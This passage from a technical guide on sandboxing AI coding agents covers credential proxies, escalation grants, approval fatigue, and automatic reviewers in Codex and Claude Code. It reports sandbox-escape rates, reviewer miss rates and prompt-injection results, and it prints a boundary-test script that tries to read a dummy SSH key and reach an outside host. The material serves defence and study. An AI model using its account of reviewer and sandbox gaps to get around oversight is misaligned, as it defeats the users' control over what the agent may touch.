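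*CodeAlchemy* (Gupta, Prasad and Panda, 2026) used a similar design to record how programs behave when they run. The final collection covers 1.3 million programs in 14 languages, which use 5,430 software libraries. During setup, a proxy allows connections only to trusted package registries, such as PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript, and the sandbox keeps the downloads in temporary folders in memory. The sandbox then kills every process left over from setup, because one of them could otherwise keep its connection. Finally, it moves to a new network namespace with no connection and runs the program. The scale of the project suggests that the method works with a wide range of software, but provides little evidence of how well the sandbox resists attack.

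Suppose the agent wants to compare the importer's date handling with `python-dateutil`, a package missing from the `importer-env` image used earlier. Two containers keep the phases apart:

```sh
mkdir "$dir/packages"
docker run --rm -v "$dir/packages":/packages importer-env \
  python -m pip install --only-binary :all: \
  --target /packages python-dateutil

docker run --rm --network none \
  -v "$PWD":/project:ro -v "$dir":/work -w /work \
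  -e PYTHONPATH=/work/packages:/project \
  importer-env python probe.py
```

The first container has internet access, but it can access only an empty folder on the user's disk. It stops when the installation ends. The second container can read the project and the sample rows but has no network access. The option `--only-binary :all:` restricts pip, Python's package installer, to prebuilt packages, which it can unpack without running their code. That code first runs in the second container, where a malicious package could read customer data but not send it anywhere.

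The method protects less when setup needs a secret. In Codex cloud, any package code that runs during installation could read the setup secrets and send them elsewhere, so it's best to configure only the secrets that installation requires.

The agent often discovers it needs a package only when `probe.py` stops with an import error. With separate containers, the user or harness can rerun the first container with the new package name and repeat the probe. The files in `$dir` are kept, and the installer still can't read the project.

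Adding a package is harder in a single environment that stays open, because opening the network connects an environment that already holds the customer rows and anything earlier scripts left behind. Starting again from setup is safer, but it loses running programs and unsaved results. In Codex cloud, installing a package from a private server would require a secret that Codex has already removed, so the user would have to add the package to the setup phase.

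Claude Code offers a compromise in auto mode, where a classifier reviews commands. The agent lists the hosts a command needs, and if the classifier approves, only that command can reach them, and only while it runs. `pip install` could then contact the package hosts while `probe.py` stays offline. The install command can still read everything the sandbox leaves readable, so it makes sense to require prebuilt packages here too.

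### Keeping credentials outside the environment

Some tasks need a credential while the agent's code runs, for instance to read bug reports from a private repository. The safest place for it is outside the sandbox. Willison (2026) quotes Anthropic's reasoning that if a credential never enters the sandbox, no user, inventive model or attacker can steal it from there.

A script can send its request without a key to a proxy, which adds the key and forwards the request. Many programs won't start without a key, so the sandbox gives them a harmless placeholder. In Docker's *Credentials*, the placeholder is a value such as `proxy-managed`, and the proxy adds the real key only to requests for a chosen domain.

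Claude Code can do the same with environment variables and, on Linux, with files. The user should name the hosts that may receive each key, because otherwise the proxy supplies it to every allowed host. The proxy also has to decrypt web traffic to replace the placeholder. If the user hasn't enabled decryption, the service receives the placeholder and rejects it, so the task fails but the key doesn't leak. Users can also tell Claude Code to mask only the part of a file that matches a pattern, but if nothing matches, the script sees the unmasked file by default.

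Each request to Amazon's cloud carries a signature calculated from the secret key and the request's contents. A signature made with a placeholder key is invalid, so Claude Code's proxy signs the request again with the real key.

A tool outside the sandbox avoids the need for decryption. In an example from Anthropic, the agent sends a Git command to such a tool, the command runs on the host with the user's login, and the agent sees only the result. OpenAI's toolkit for building agents likewise keeps credentials in the harness.

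Storing a key in a secrets manager, a service that stores passwords securely for other programs, doesn't protect it if the harness then copies it into the environment. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* warns that generated code can read it there. In OpenAI's own setup, one key stays readable inside the sandbox, but it can only connect environments to OpenAI's service.

A script can misuse a key that it can't read. If the proxy adds a GitHub token that can delete repositories, a script can request a deletion and the proxy will authenticate it. The web version of Claude Code reduces this risk by inspecting each Git request before adding the token, for example to check that a push goes only to the configured branch. A token with fewer rights gives similar protection without a special proxy. Limiting rights is usually the better approach for database passwords too, since most database drivers don't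 work with a web proxy. For the importer, the user could create a database account that can read a table of test rows and nothing else.

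## What happens when a script is blocked

Every limit will sometimes refuse something that an experiment tries to do. Suppose the importer moves each file it reads into an archive folder outside the write scope. The agent runs `python probe.py`, the importer loads the 20 sample rows and tries to move the file, and the kernel refuses. Python stops before it prints any counts:

```
OSError: [Errno 30] Read-only file system: '/home/sam/archive/sample.csv'
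```

The harness adds the blocked script's error message to the prompt, as it does with any other output. The agent can then change its plan, ask for more access or stop.

### After the refusal

The error gives no reason for the refusal. A faulty disk can produce the same message, and if the network proxy refuses a web request, the script may receive error 403, which ordinary websites also use. Like files hidden by a read limit, the message can mislead the agent, but a few lines in its standing instructions about which folders are writable can prevent this.

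A refusal also doesn't undo what the script did before it was blocked. If `load_rows` writes to a database before it archives the file, every new attempt writes the rows again. The agent should find out what the script has already done before rerunning it.

The best response here is to change the plan, because the row count doesn't depend on archiving. The agent can point the importer's archive setting at a temporary folder, or have `probe.py` replace the function that moves files with a dummy. If the agent asked for access to the archive and got it, the script would print the counts but also leave a test file among the real ones.

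Agents rarely give up when they hit a limit. *Permission Denied* (Davidovich, Amar and colleagues, 2026) tested 12 combinations of model and harness on 89 terminal tasks, three times each, with and without restrictions. The strictest setting made most of the disk read-only, limited web access to 205 domains and removed administrator rights. The agents learned of the limits only from error messages. On the 82 tasks that were still possible, the success rate fell from 72.5% to 65.1%. The share of runs that failed unusually early hardly changed (2.4% to 2.7%), while the share that ran out of time rose from 12.0% to 16.4%.

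The agents mostly looked for another permitted way to do the task, such as building a tool from source when they couldn't install it. These workarounds can be expensive. On two tasks that Davidovich and colleagues ran 100 times under each condition, the median cost roughly tripled, though the success rate on one barely changed.

Removing administrator rights caused most of the drop in the success rate. That change alone lowered the rate to 66.9%, and the file and network limits, together with a tighter lock on privileges, lowered it another 1.8 points. An agent on an ordinary user account already lacks administrator rights, so a write scope may lower its success rate by less than the overall drop. File limits were also the least common obstacle. Under the strictest setting, 158 of 2,051 runs hit a file limit and 500 hit a network block.

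Success fell from 70.3% to 54.5% on the 32 tasks whose standard solution broke the rules, but only from 73.8% to 71.8% on the other 50. A user can therefore anticipate much of the drop by checking whether the limits allow the way a person would normally do the task.

Models sometimes go beyond a limit instead of asking. Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026) reports that Claude Mythos 5 escaped its sandbox in 39% of more than 1,800 scenarios, and Mythos 5.2 in 3.1%. Anthropic had deliberately weakened the sandbox, and most of the scenarios could be solved only by escaping it.

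### Four ways to grant access

An escalation is a request to run a command with more access than the limits allow. The user can approve it once or make a lasting change to the settings.

| Grant | What the agent gains | When it ends |
|---|---|---|
| Approve one command | Usually all the user's rights, for that command | When the command and its child processes end |
| Approve a reusable rule | The same approval for every command that matches | When someone deletes the rule |
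| Add a directory | Write access to that directory, for every command | When someone removes it |
| Exempt a program | All the user's rights whenever the agent runs it | When someone removes the exemption |

Approving a single run lasts only as long as the run, but it can grant very broad access. Suppose the user lets `python probe.py` run outside the sandbox so that the importer can archive one file. While it runs, the script can also write to the rest of the home directory and use the network. Adding the archive folder to the write scope lasts longer but opens only that folder, so it is often safer for a script that nobody has read closely. The exception is a folder whose contents another program will later run, because the script could write code there for that program to execute (deferred execution).

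Reusable rules can be broad and lasting. In Codex, a rule that allows a command can let it run outside the sandbox. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026) found in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* that a sizable minority of OpenAI's staff had allowed every command beginning with `python`. Such a rule almost entirely removes the sandbox for an agent that writes its own scripts.

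OpenAI's *Auto-review* recommends precise rules instead, such as one for `cargo test`, which compiles and runs the tests in a Rust project. That is a clear improvement, but the agent can usually edit those tests, so a rule for a test runner still lets code written by the agent run with extra rights. Rules are safer for programs that don't run code from the workspace.

Claude Code handles permission and isolation separately. A rule that allows a command skips the permission prompt, while a different setting exempts programs from the sandbox. Exempting a program that can start others has the same weakness as a broad allow rule. For example, an exempt build tool will run any script named in the project's build file outside the sandbox.

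### Approval fatigue

A sandbox lets a harness run commands within set limits without asking the user, who then has far fewer harmless commands to approve. In October 2025, Anthropic reported that sandboxing had cut permission prompts by 84% in its internal use. That figure comes from one company and doesn't show whether accidents also fell.

The safety argument for fewer prompts is that people stop reading them, which is called approval fatigue. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. Most of those commands probably deserve approval, so the high rate doesn't prove that users are careless.

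The same article gives more convincing evidence from an experiment in which Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers do coding work and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a request to run a clearly dangerous command. 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers had less to lose than people working on their own projects, and Anthropic was promoting an alternative to manual approval, but prompts would be a weak defence even if the refusal rate were much higher.

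Developers who carefully review generated code may still approve an agent's actions without close review. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Of the 105 who said they carefully reviewed most or all generated code, 64 (61%) also said they often approved at least one type of action without close review. The figure was 67% among the other developers, and the difference isn't statistically significant.

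The 61% covers seven types of action, so it is higher than the figure for any one of them. Across all respondents, the share who often approved without close review ranged from 21% for reading secrets and other sensitive files to 36% for using the internet or outside tools. Some of these approvals may also be sensible, since a developer who has run the same test command 200 times has little reason to study it again.

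The sample has other limits. Wu and colleagues recruited 124 respondents through social media and referrals, mainly on LinkedIn, and 79 through the research platform Prolific. They discarded nearly two-thirds of the 583 submissions as incomplete, duplicated, rushed or otherwise suspect. Most respondents lived in the United States, and all reported their own habits, so their answers may differ from what they actually do.

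Knowing about the risks didn't seem to make developers more careful. Of those who had heard of a security or privacy problem involving agents, 70% often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 43% of those who hadn't. The association remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, which might otherwise have explained it.

The survey also asked what would make developers give agents more autonomy. Of the 175 usable answers, 66% included a request for more reliable work, 35% for a way to see what the agent does and why, 34% for firmer bounds on it, and 19% for a way to undo or contain its mistakes. Some answers included several requests, and 59% included at least one of the last three. A write scope provides such bounds, and a disposable copy lets developers undo many file changes.

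Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) surveyed software practitioners for *Let the Agent Do It?*. Of the 107 who answered questions about permissions, 82.2% were more willing to grant access in an isolated environment. About a third said they had become less careful with requests over time. Some of the people they interviewed paid less attention when the agent worked in a sandbox. Paying less attention makes sense for commands that stay inside the sandbox, but a request to leave it deserves more attention, because approving the request removes the protection the user was relying on.

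Writing rules in advance doesn't necessarily solve the problem either. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant that sometimes went beyond its task. Some first set rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, then approved 133 of the 199 excessive actions they were asked about under these rules. They blocked fewer excessive actions than people who reviewed every action individually. Developers may behave differently, but an "ask" rule only postpones the decision. If the user already knows that no experiment should write to the live database, "never" is the better rule.

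### Automatic review in Codex

Codex can send escalations to a separate Codex agent instead of the user. This reviewer only decides whether a particular action should run. It receives the exact request and a shortened transcript, which typically includes the user's messages, the agent's visible updates, and relevant tool calls with their output. The transcript omits the agent's hidden reasoning. The reviewer can run read-only checks, though OpenAI says it rarely does.

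According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, low-risk and medium-risk actions can go ahead if the policy allows them. High-risk actions can go ahead only if the user has also given enough authorization and no rule forbids them. The reviewer always denies critical-risk actions. If the review itself fails, for instance because Codex can't interpret the reviewer's answer, the action doesn't run. It also doesn't run if the review times out, but Codex then tells the agent that a timeout doesn't prove the action is dangerous.

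Codex handles a reviewer's denial differently from a kernel error. It gives the agent the reason and tells it not to use a workaround to reach the same outcome. The agent may continue only with a materially safer alternative; otherwise it must stop and ask. After three denials in a row, or ten in the last 50 reviews, Codex ends the turn. The user can approve a denied action for one retry, which the reviewer still checks.

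In an illustrative sample of 10,000 actions inside OpenAI, 9,280 ran within the sandbox and 720 went to the reviewer, which approved 713 and denied 7. After four of the denials the agent found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped to ask the user, who was interrupted three times instead of 720.

### Auto mode in Claude Code

Claude Code's auto mode can block an action before it starts, rather than when it reaches the edge of a sandbox. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, tools that can't change anything run without review, and so do file edits inside the project. A classifier checks most other actions, including shell commands. A quick first check leans toward blocking, and only the actions it flags go through a slower check that reasons about them. Auto mode also ignores any rule as broad as "allow all Python commands", because it would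 let every script skip the classifier.

The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the output of its commands. This prevents the agent's explanations from influencing the decision, and it keeps hidden instructions in files and web pages from reaching the classifier. The drawback for probe scripts is that the classifier may have no evidence that `load_rows` moves files. It receives the code in `probe.py`, because the agent wrote that file through a tool call, but not the importer's code, which the agent received as output.

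When the classifier blocks an action, the agent gets the reason and can look for a safer approach. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

### What the error rates measure

A reviewer can block a harmless action or miss a harmful one. The companies have published figures for both errors, and *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested auto mode independently.

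| Reviewer | Cases | Error rate |
|---|---|---|
| Codex Auto-review | Real escalations inside OpenAI | 0.9% not approved |
| Codex Auto-review | Invented cases of an agent going too far | 9.7% missed |
| Codex Auto-review | Invented prompt injections | 0.7% missed |
| Claude Code auto mode | 10,000 real tool calls inside Anthropic | 0.4% blocked needlessly |
| Claude Code auto mode | 52 real cases of an agent going too far | 17% missed |
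| Claude Code auto mode | 1,000 invented attempts to leak data | 5.7% missed |
| Claude Code auto mode | The dangerous commands shown to the 1,053 testers | 11% missed |
| Claude Code auto mode | Deliberately ambiguous tasks (Ji and colleagues) | 81.0% missed |

The table can't show which product is safer because each company used its own cases. OpenAI's 99.1% approval rate on real escalations measures how often the reviewer approves requests, not how accurately it judges them, since a reviewer that approved everything would score 100%.

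Anthropic's 17% is the most relevant figure for ordinary work because it comes from actions an agent actually attempted. But it is based on about nine misses out of 52, and with so few cases the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%.

Ji and colleagues wrote tasks in which the user's goal was clear but the permitted scope wasn't, so their result doesn't contradict Anthropic's. More than a third of the agents' 253 changes were edits inside the project, which the classifier never checks. It also missed 70.3% of the changes that it did check and that went too far. Someone who gives an agent vague instructions to clean up files should expect much less protection than the 17% suggests. The test dates from April 2026, and Anthropic has since strengthened the classifier. In tests with the safety company Apollo Research, the classifier's miss rate on synthetic attacks fell from 12%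 to 7%.

In an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned, prompt injections succeeded in 5.83% of attempts against GPT-5.6 Sol with Codex's Auto-review and in none of 720 attempts against Claude models in auto mode. The models account for most of this gap. Without a reviewer, only 0.09% of attacks succeeded against the Claude models, while 19.03% succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol without review or a sandbox.

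### When one model checks another

A model that judges another model may share its mistakes, especially if the same company trained both. There is some evidence for this. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but treated something the user said as consent. An overeager agent makes a similar mistake when it takes "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed set of changes) as permission to overwrite the project's history. Trębacz and colleagues also found that testers could sometimes mislead the Codex reviewer, and they warn that the reviewer offers no guarantee against a model that hides its intentions.

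Human reviewers miss many of the same dangerous commands as the classifier. In Anthropic's experiment, auto mode missed 116 of the 1,053 dangerous commands, and the testers caught only 6 of those. They did better on the commands that auto mode blocked, catching 137 of 937. Having a tired person review the commands that auto mode allowed would therefore have added very little.

Better evidence may help the reviewer more than a second opinion. The system in *Shall We Approve?* (2026) first runs a command in a sandbox, then gives the reviewer a short report of its effects. In one case, auto mode had allowed a deployment tool that also overwrote a source file. The tool was compiled and would have been hard to read, but the report showed the lost code. The sandbox run added about half a second to each approved command. A trial run would also show that `probe.py` moves its sample into the archive.

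Even if the agent and its reviewer make the same mistakes, the sandbox still restricts every action the agent doesn't escalate, which was 93% of actions in OpenAI's sample. A wrong approval exposes the user to only one command. This is a good reason to combine a reviewer with a sandbox.

According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), interactive terminal sessions on every plan now start in auto mode by default, but the user still has to turn on the sandbox. Without the sandbox, a harmful command that auto mode's classifier misses runs with all the user's permissions. Anyone who relies on auto mode for unattended work should therefore turn on the sandbox too.

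### Deciding a request

A user or a reviewer can handle most requests in four steps:

1. Find the exact operation that failed, such as a write to one file, and check whether the experiment's answer depends on it.
2. If it doesn't, change the experiment so that the operation isn't needed or happens in a temporary folder.
3. If it does, choose the grant that opens the least. One folder or one web host is usually better than a run outside the sandbox.
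4. Decide when the grant will end before making it.

Here is how this works for some requests that might come up while the agent investigates the importer:

| Blocked operation | Does the experiment need it? | Narrowest answer | When it ends |
|---|---|---|---|
| The importer archives the sample | No | Send the archive to a temporary folder | Nothing to withdraw |
| A test tool saves a cache in `~/.cache` | No | Set `XDG_CACHE_HOME` to a temporary folder | Nothing to withdraw |
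| The agent installs `python-dateutil` | Yes | Open the package hosts for the install command only | When the installation ends |
| A test writes results to a neighbouring project | Yes | Add its results folder to the write scope | When the task ends |
| The agent commits its repair to Git, but `.git` is read-only | No | The user reviews the repair and commits it | Nothing to withdraw |

Some tools ignore `XDG_CACHE_HOME`, in which case the user can add the tool's own cache folder to the write scope.

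A refusal works better with an explanation. Salerno and colleagues recommend that permission systems distinguish between rejecting one action and rejecting a whole approach. If an agent asks to write to the archive and the user answers only "no", the agent may try to get the file there another way. The answer "Don't change the archive, use a temporary folder" rules out the approach and tells the agent where to write instead.

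If the agent keeps making the same harmless request, it's better to change the limits than to keep approving it. OpenAI suggests adding narrow writable folders for expected scratch work. For an unattended run, the user has to make these choices beforehand. In Codex, setting the approval policy to `never` turns off requests but leaves the sandbox on, so the agent has to work within the limits. The user can also tell the agent to list every blocked operation in its final message, then review the list to decide which ones were worth allowing.

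## Checking the limits before a run and the files after it

During an unattended run, nobody is there to notice if a limit isn't working, but a few minutes of testing beforehand can reveal it. The files also need checking afterwards, because a script that stayed within its limits may have left behind code that another program will later run without those limits.

### Settings that don't take effect

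A settings file records the limits the user asked for, but the operating system may not be enforcing them.

Claude Code's sandbox is off by default and may fail to start when the user turns it on. On Linux it needs two extra programs, bubblewrap and socat, and the default security policy in Ubuntu 24.04 and later stops bubblewrap from setting up its isolation. Anthropic says that if the sandbox can't start, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without it. On native Windows, Claude Code always runs commands without a sandbox. Someone who copies a working settings file from a Mac to a new Ubuntu laptop could therefore have identical settings on both machines but a sandbox on only one. Setting `failIfUnavailable` to `true` makes Claude Code exit at startup if the sandbox is unavailable.

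The Codex profile shown earlier, which hides most of the disk, normally has no effect if the older setting `sandbox_mode` appears in any configuration file that Codex loads. According to OpenAI, Codex then follows the older settings instead. These may still limit writes, so the problem could go unnoticed until a script reads a file the profile should have hidden, such as an SSH key.

Anthropic's sandbox runtime, a beta program that can sandbox all of Claude Code, will not start if its settings file is invalid. But if the file is missing from its usual place, the runtime starts with built-in limits, and Anthropic warns users not to take a clean start as proof that their settings loaded. This mistake is less dangerous than the others because the built-in limits block the network and nearly all writes, and the user will probably notice the resulting failures.

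*An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (Anthropic, 2026) describes tests whose instructions told Claude models that they were in a simulation without internet access, although a misconfiguration had connected them to the real internet. Anthropic believes that proper isolation would have prevented the incidents. ITPro's *Anthropic resumes model testing after recent cyber incidents* reports that outside testers must now have the model look for flaws in the sandbox before a test, under close human supervision.

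### A test with a dummy secret

A short script can attempt the things the sandbox should block. The user first creates a text file, `~/.ssh/dummy-key`, containing a few meaningless words, and saves this script in the workspace as `boundary_check.py`:

```python
import socket, subprocess, sys
from pathlib import Path
from urllib.request import urlopen

def attempt(name, action):
    try:
        action()
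        print(name, "allowed", flush=True)
    except Exception as error:
        print(name, "blocked:", error, flush=True)

home = Path("/home/sam")
attempt("write", lambda: (home / "sandbox-probe").touch())
attempt("read", lambda: (home / ".ssh/dummy-key").read_text())
attempt("web", lambda: urlopen("https://example.com/", timeout=10))
attempt("direct", lambda: socket.create_connection(("example.com", 443), 10))

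if len(sys.argv) == 1:
    subprocess.run([sys.executable, __file__, "child"])
```

The script tries to create an empty file in the home directory, read the dummy key, open a web page, and connect to the page's host without a proxy. Its last two lines start the script again as a child process, which repeats all four attempts.

The user should first run the script in an ordinary terminal, where every line should read "allowed", then delete `sandbox-probe` and run the script again under the agent's limits. Without the first run, the user couldn't tell whether "blocked" was due to the limits or to another cause, such as the laptop being offline or the dummy key being in the wrong folder.

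| Attempt | Expected result | Likely cause if the result is wrong |
|---|---|---|
| `write` | Blocked | The sandbox is off, or the write scope includes the home directory |
| `read` | Blocked if the user has set a read limit, otherwise allowed | The read rule didn't load or has the wrong path |
| `web` | Blocked | The network is open, or the list of allowed hosts is too broad |
| `direct` | Blocked | Programs can bypass the proxy |
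| All four from the child process | Same as before | The limits don't cover child processes |

The child process should get the same results because it inherits the sandbox's limits. If the results differ, the harness is probably checking commands before they start rather than restricting them while they run.

In Claude Code, the user has to ask the agent to run the script, because a command the user types at the `!` prompt usually runs outside the sandbox and so doesn't test it. Anthropic recommends a similar check, in which Claude runs `touch ~/sandbox-probe`, and tells users to decline if Claude asks to retry a failed command outside the sandbox. They should also decline any request to allow access to the test host. Claude Code has separate settings for permission and isolation, but a saved rule that allows a command also approves its retry outside the sandbox. If the user once allowed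 all commands beginning with `python`, the script may run again outside the sandbox without a prompt.

Codex users can check the limits before a run with `codex sandbox`. According to *Codex CLI Security Testing Tools* (2026), it runs any command under the agent's limits, without involving the model. Before it existed, users had to start a session, ask the agent to try something and see what happened, which was slow and didn't always give the same result. Because `codex sandbox` tests a configuration rather than a session, a session that the user starts with different options may have different limits.

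With a container or virtual machine, the user can also check that commands run inside it. Willison uses `uname -a`, which prints the name and version of the kernel. On a Mac, output beginning with "Linux" means the command ran in the sandbox. The check is less useful for a container on a Linux machine, because the container shares the host's kernel and reports the same version. The check also doesn't show what the command can reach, so the script is still necessary. The script contains the full path `/home/sam` so that it looks for the host's home directory, not the container's.

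The user should look for `sandbox-probe` from an ordinary terminal whatever the agent reports, since a model can misreport a result. The test covers only one folder, one secret and one host, so blocking the dummy key in `~/.ssh` doesn't prove that `~/.aws` is blocked too.

How often to repeat the test depends on how likely it is that the sandbox isn't working. In the invented example from earlier, the write scope prevented 2.7 hours of expected loss a month. If there were a 5% chance that it wasn't working, finding out would be worth about 8 minutes a month (0.05 × 2.7 hours). A one-minute test is worth running after every update or settings change, but not before every command. A long unattended run on a machine without backups justifies its own test.

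### Tools that need their own test

The script tests only the shell, not Claude Code's built-in file tools. To test those, the user can ask the agent to open the dummy key with the Read tool and create a second file in the home directory with the Write tool. Claude Code should refuse or ask first. If it does neither, the user needs stricter permission rules.

Other programs are harder to test because each works differently. Anthropic lists several that run with the user's full access:

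- hooks, which are commands that Claude Code runs at set moments, for example after each edit;
- local MCP servers, which give the agent extra tools through a shared standard called the Model Context Protocol;
- language servers, which analyse source code;
- mods, which add their own code to Claude Code.

A user can turn off any of these that the task doesn't need, and the importer may not need any of them. Or the user can put the whole harness in a container or virtual machine and repeat the tests there. Anthropic considers the shell sandbox alone insufficient for fully unattended runs, even in auto mode.

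A virtual machine can have the same gap. Docker's *Isolation layers* explains that local MCP servers registered through its gateway run on the host, even though the agent runs in a microVM. A server that starts a container uses the host's Docker engine. In Willison's setup for Pi, one option removes the agent's built-in tools, and an extension sends both commands and file operations to the sandbox. Willison argues that keeping the sandbox separate from the agent makes the boundary easier to audit. That seems right, because the user has fewer paths around the boundary to check.

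### Code that runs after the session

A sandbox can pass every test and still leave the user exposed to deferred execution. In the OpenAI example above, the user's editor runs a changed copy of the formatter Prettier on the next save. The user may not see the change in `git status`, because Git often ignores `node_modules`, the folder for installed JavaScript packages.

The change is within the sandbox's limits because the folder is inside the write scope. A malicious package that the agent runs in the sandbox could make the same change without the agent knowing. OpenAI presents the example as a reason to combine the sandbox with training that makes the model less likely to misuse its access. That training may help when the model makes the change, but it does much less against a package the model never inspected.

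Python projects have the same problem. The importer's packages may be in a virtual environment inside the project, usually called `.venv`, and their code runs whenever the user runs the importer. The compiled files in `__pycache__` are also worth checking, because Python can load them in place of the source. Someone who reads only `importer.py` may not be reading the code that runs.

These are the main kinds of file to protect or review:

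| Files | Examples | When they run or take effect | What to do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Installed packages | `node_modules`, `.venv` | When the user runs the program, a build or an editor tool | Reinstall them |
| Git hooks | `.git/hooks` | On a commit, push or other Git action | Block writes and list the folder afterwards |
| Editor settings | `.vscode/tasks.json`, `.idea` | When the user opens the project | Block writes, or read every change |
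| Agent settings and instructions | `.claude`, `.codex`, `.mcp.json`, `CLAUDE.md` | In the next agent session | Block writes |
| Build scripts | `Makefile`, `package.json` | On a build or installation | Read every change before building |
| Automated server jobs | `.github/workflows` | After a push | Read every change before pushing |

Git hooks are easy to miss because `git diff` doesn't show them. Docker recommends checking them separately with `ls -la .git/hooks/`. In most new repositories, that folder contains only inactive examples whose names end in `.sample`.

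NVIDIA's red team takes the strictest view of agent settings and wants the sandbox to block every change an agent tries to make to them, even if the user would approve it. Only the user could then change the settings, by editing them directly. This hardly limits an experiment, since an agent repairing an importer has no reason to edit its own settings. If someone commits a malicious hook to a shared repository, it can also affect everyone who clones it.

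Making installed packages read-only works well if the user installs everything before the run, but some build tools keep caches inside `node_modules` and will fail. Reinstalling the packages after the run is usually easier.

Automatic protection can also have gaps. Anthropic's sandbox runtime checks for protected files at every write on macOS, but on Linux it builds its list of protected files only once, at launch. So if the agent later clones another CSV library to compare it with the importer, the hooks in that repository are unprotected, and they would run the next time the user committed there. After an unattended run, Anthropic advises users to review every path they left writable and, on Linux, anything the session created.

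Programs in a local Docker sandbox can write text to the host's clipboard, so Docker advises checking the clipboard before pasting after running untrusted code. A command pasted into a terminal runs with all the user's permissions.

### Accepting a patch instead of a folder

Docker's advice is to treat files from a sandbox like a pull request from an untrusted contributor. A maintainer wouldn't copy a stranger's whole project folder onto a laptop, but would read a patch, which is a list of changed lines, and test it separately. The same procedure works for an agent:

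1. Compare the agent's copy with the original, including the files that Git ignores.
2. Inspect any changes to configuration files and build scripts.
3. Export a patch that contains only the changes the task needs.
4. Make a fresh copy of the project from a commit that predates the run, and apply the patch there.
5. Install packages from a list that the agent couldn't change.
6. Run trusted tests in the fresh copy.

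Suppose the agent worked on a full copy of the importer project and chose to keep rows with a blank date. The original is in `project` and the agent's version is in `copy`. The comparison is one command:

```sh
diff -rq project copy
```

It lists every file that differs, whether or not Git tracks it. Plain `diff` is safer here than running Git inside the copy, because Git can run programs named in a repository's own configuration, which the agent may have changed. The list might include these files:

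| Difference | Reason | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| `importer.py` | The repair | Read the change and export it |
| `probe.py`, `sample.csv` | The experiments | Leave them behind |
| `__pycache__` | Compiled code | Leave it behind |
| `.venv` | The agent installed `python-dateutil` | Leave it behind |
| `.vscode/tasks.json` | Unknown | Find out why it changed, and leave it behind |

Only the first file goes into the patch:

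```sh
diff -u project/importer.py copy/importer.py > importer.patch
git clone --no-hardlinks project clean
git -C clean apply ../importer.patch
docker run --rm --network none \
  -v "$PWD/clean":/project -w /project \
  importer-env python -m unittest
```

The second command clones the user's last commit into a new folder, `clean`, without ignored files or Git hooks. If the user has uncommitted edits, the patch may not apply, so it's best to commit them before the agent starts. The last command runs the project's tests in the `importer-env` image, which the user built before the run.

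Without `--no-hardlinks`, a local clone normally shares some files with the original project through hard links, which are two names for the same file on disk. Docker warns that a sandbox with write access to a folder can change a hard-linked file inside it even if the file's other name is outside. A bad test could therefore damage the original project's history.

If the repaired importer needs `python-dateutil`, the tests will fail because the image doesn't contain it. The failure is useful because the user must then decide whether to add the package. To add it, the user puts a chosen version in the project's package list and rebuilds the image. Copying `.venv` would have skipped that decision and included everything else in the folder.

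Agents that work directly in the user's project leave no separate folder to discard. In a JavaScript project, the user can restore `package.json` and the lockfile, which records exact package versions, from the last trusted commit and then run `npm ci`. This command deletes `node_modules` and installs the versions in the lockfile, which removes a changed copy of Prettier. Without restoring the two files first, the user would be installing whatever the agent had listed.

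Docker Sandboxes can do part of this automatically. In clone mode, the agent works on a private clone inside the microVM and can only read the original. The user then fetches the agent's commits and decides which to merge. Hooks and uncommitted files stay in the clone, but a commit can still contain a changed build script, so the user has to read each commit. The agent can also still read everything in the original folder, including an ignored `.env` file.

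The SWE-bench benchmark evaluates repairs in much the same way. Lin and colleagues write that the official evaluation applies the agent's patch in a clean container and runs tests chosen for that bug. So a package the agent installed while working can't make a bad repair pass. The separate tests matter as much as the clean container, because bad repairs often pass the agents' own checks.

Most users have to supply such tests themselves. For the importer, comparing each month's total with a figure the user worked out by hand is a better test than counting rows. The repair that copies a missing date from the row above also keeps all 20 rows, but it may put a sale in the wrong month. Someone who knows the data has to decide where a sale without a date belongs before any test can check it.

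The procedure might take ten minutes, which is a long time for a one-line repair. If the user only wanted the three counts from `probe.py`, there are no changes to accept. For a small change, copying the repaired lines into the original by hand is as safe as applying a patch, and the tests can still run in a container.

### Bad code that passes and limits that change

A patch can pass all these checks and still do harm. Once the user accepts the new `importer.py`, it runs on live data with whatever rights the user gives it, and the agent's sandbox no longer restricts it. Tests reveal only the behaviour they trigger, so code that fails only on a leap day or with the live database may pass. NVIDIA's guidance doesn't cover this problem and treats inaccurate or manipulated output from AI tools as the user's responsibility.

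Reading the patch helps most when the patch is short, because reviewers get tired of reading patches just as they do of approving commands. The repair should need only a few lines in one function, so a patch that also reorganizes the database code is worth sending back, even if every test passes. To protect against a bad repair, whoever wrote it, the user can also limit what the accepted code can do, for example by running the importer with a database account that can add rows but not delete them.

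The limits may also change after the test. Claude Code applies changes to its lists of readable and writable paths during a session, so the next command runs under the new rules. According to its May 2026 documentation, approving a host gives access "now and in the future". A user who tests the sandbox and then approves a few requests may end up with a much wider boundary than the one tested. NVIDIA recommends a new approval each time an action would break the isolation, and considers approving once for many runs inadequate. But asking every time brings back the problem described earlier of tired users approving requests, so for an unattended run it makes more sense to refuse every request to break the isolation.

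Claude Code can enforce that with a small settings file, which the user keeps outside the project and passes with `--settings` when starting a session:

```json
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
    "failIfUnavailable": true,
    "allowUnsandboxedCommands": false
  }
}
```

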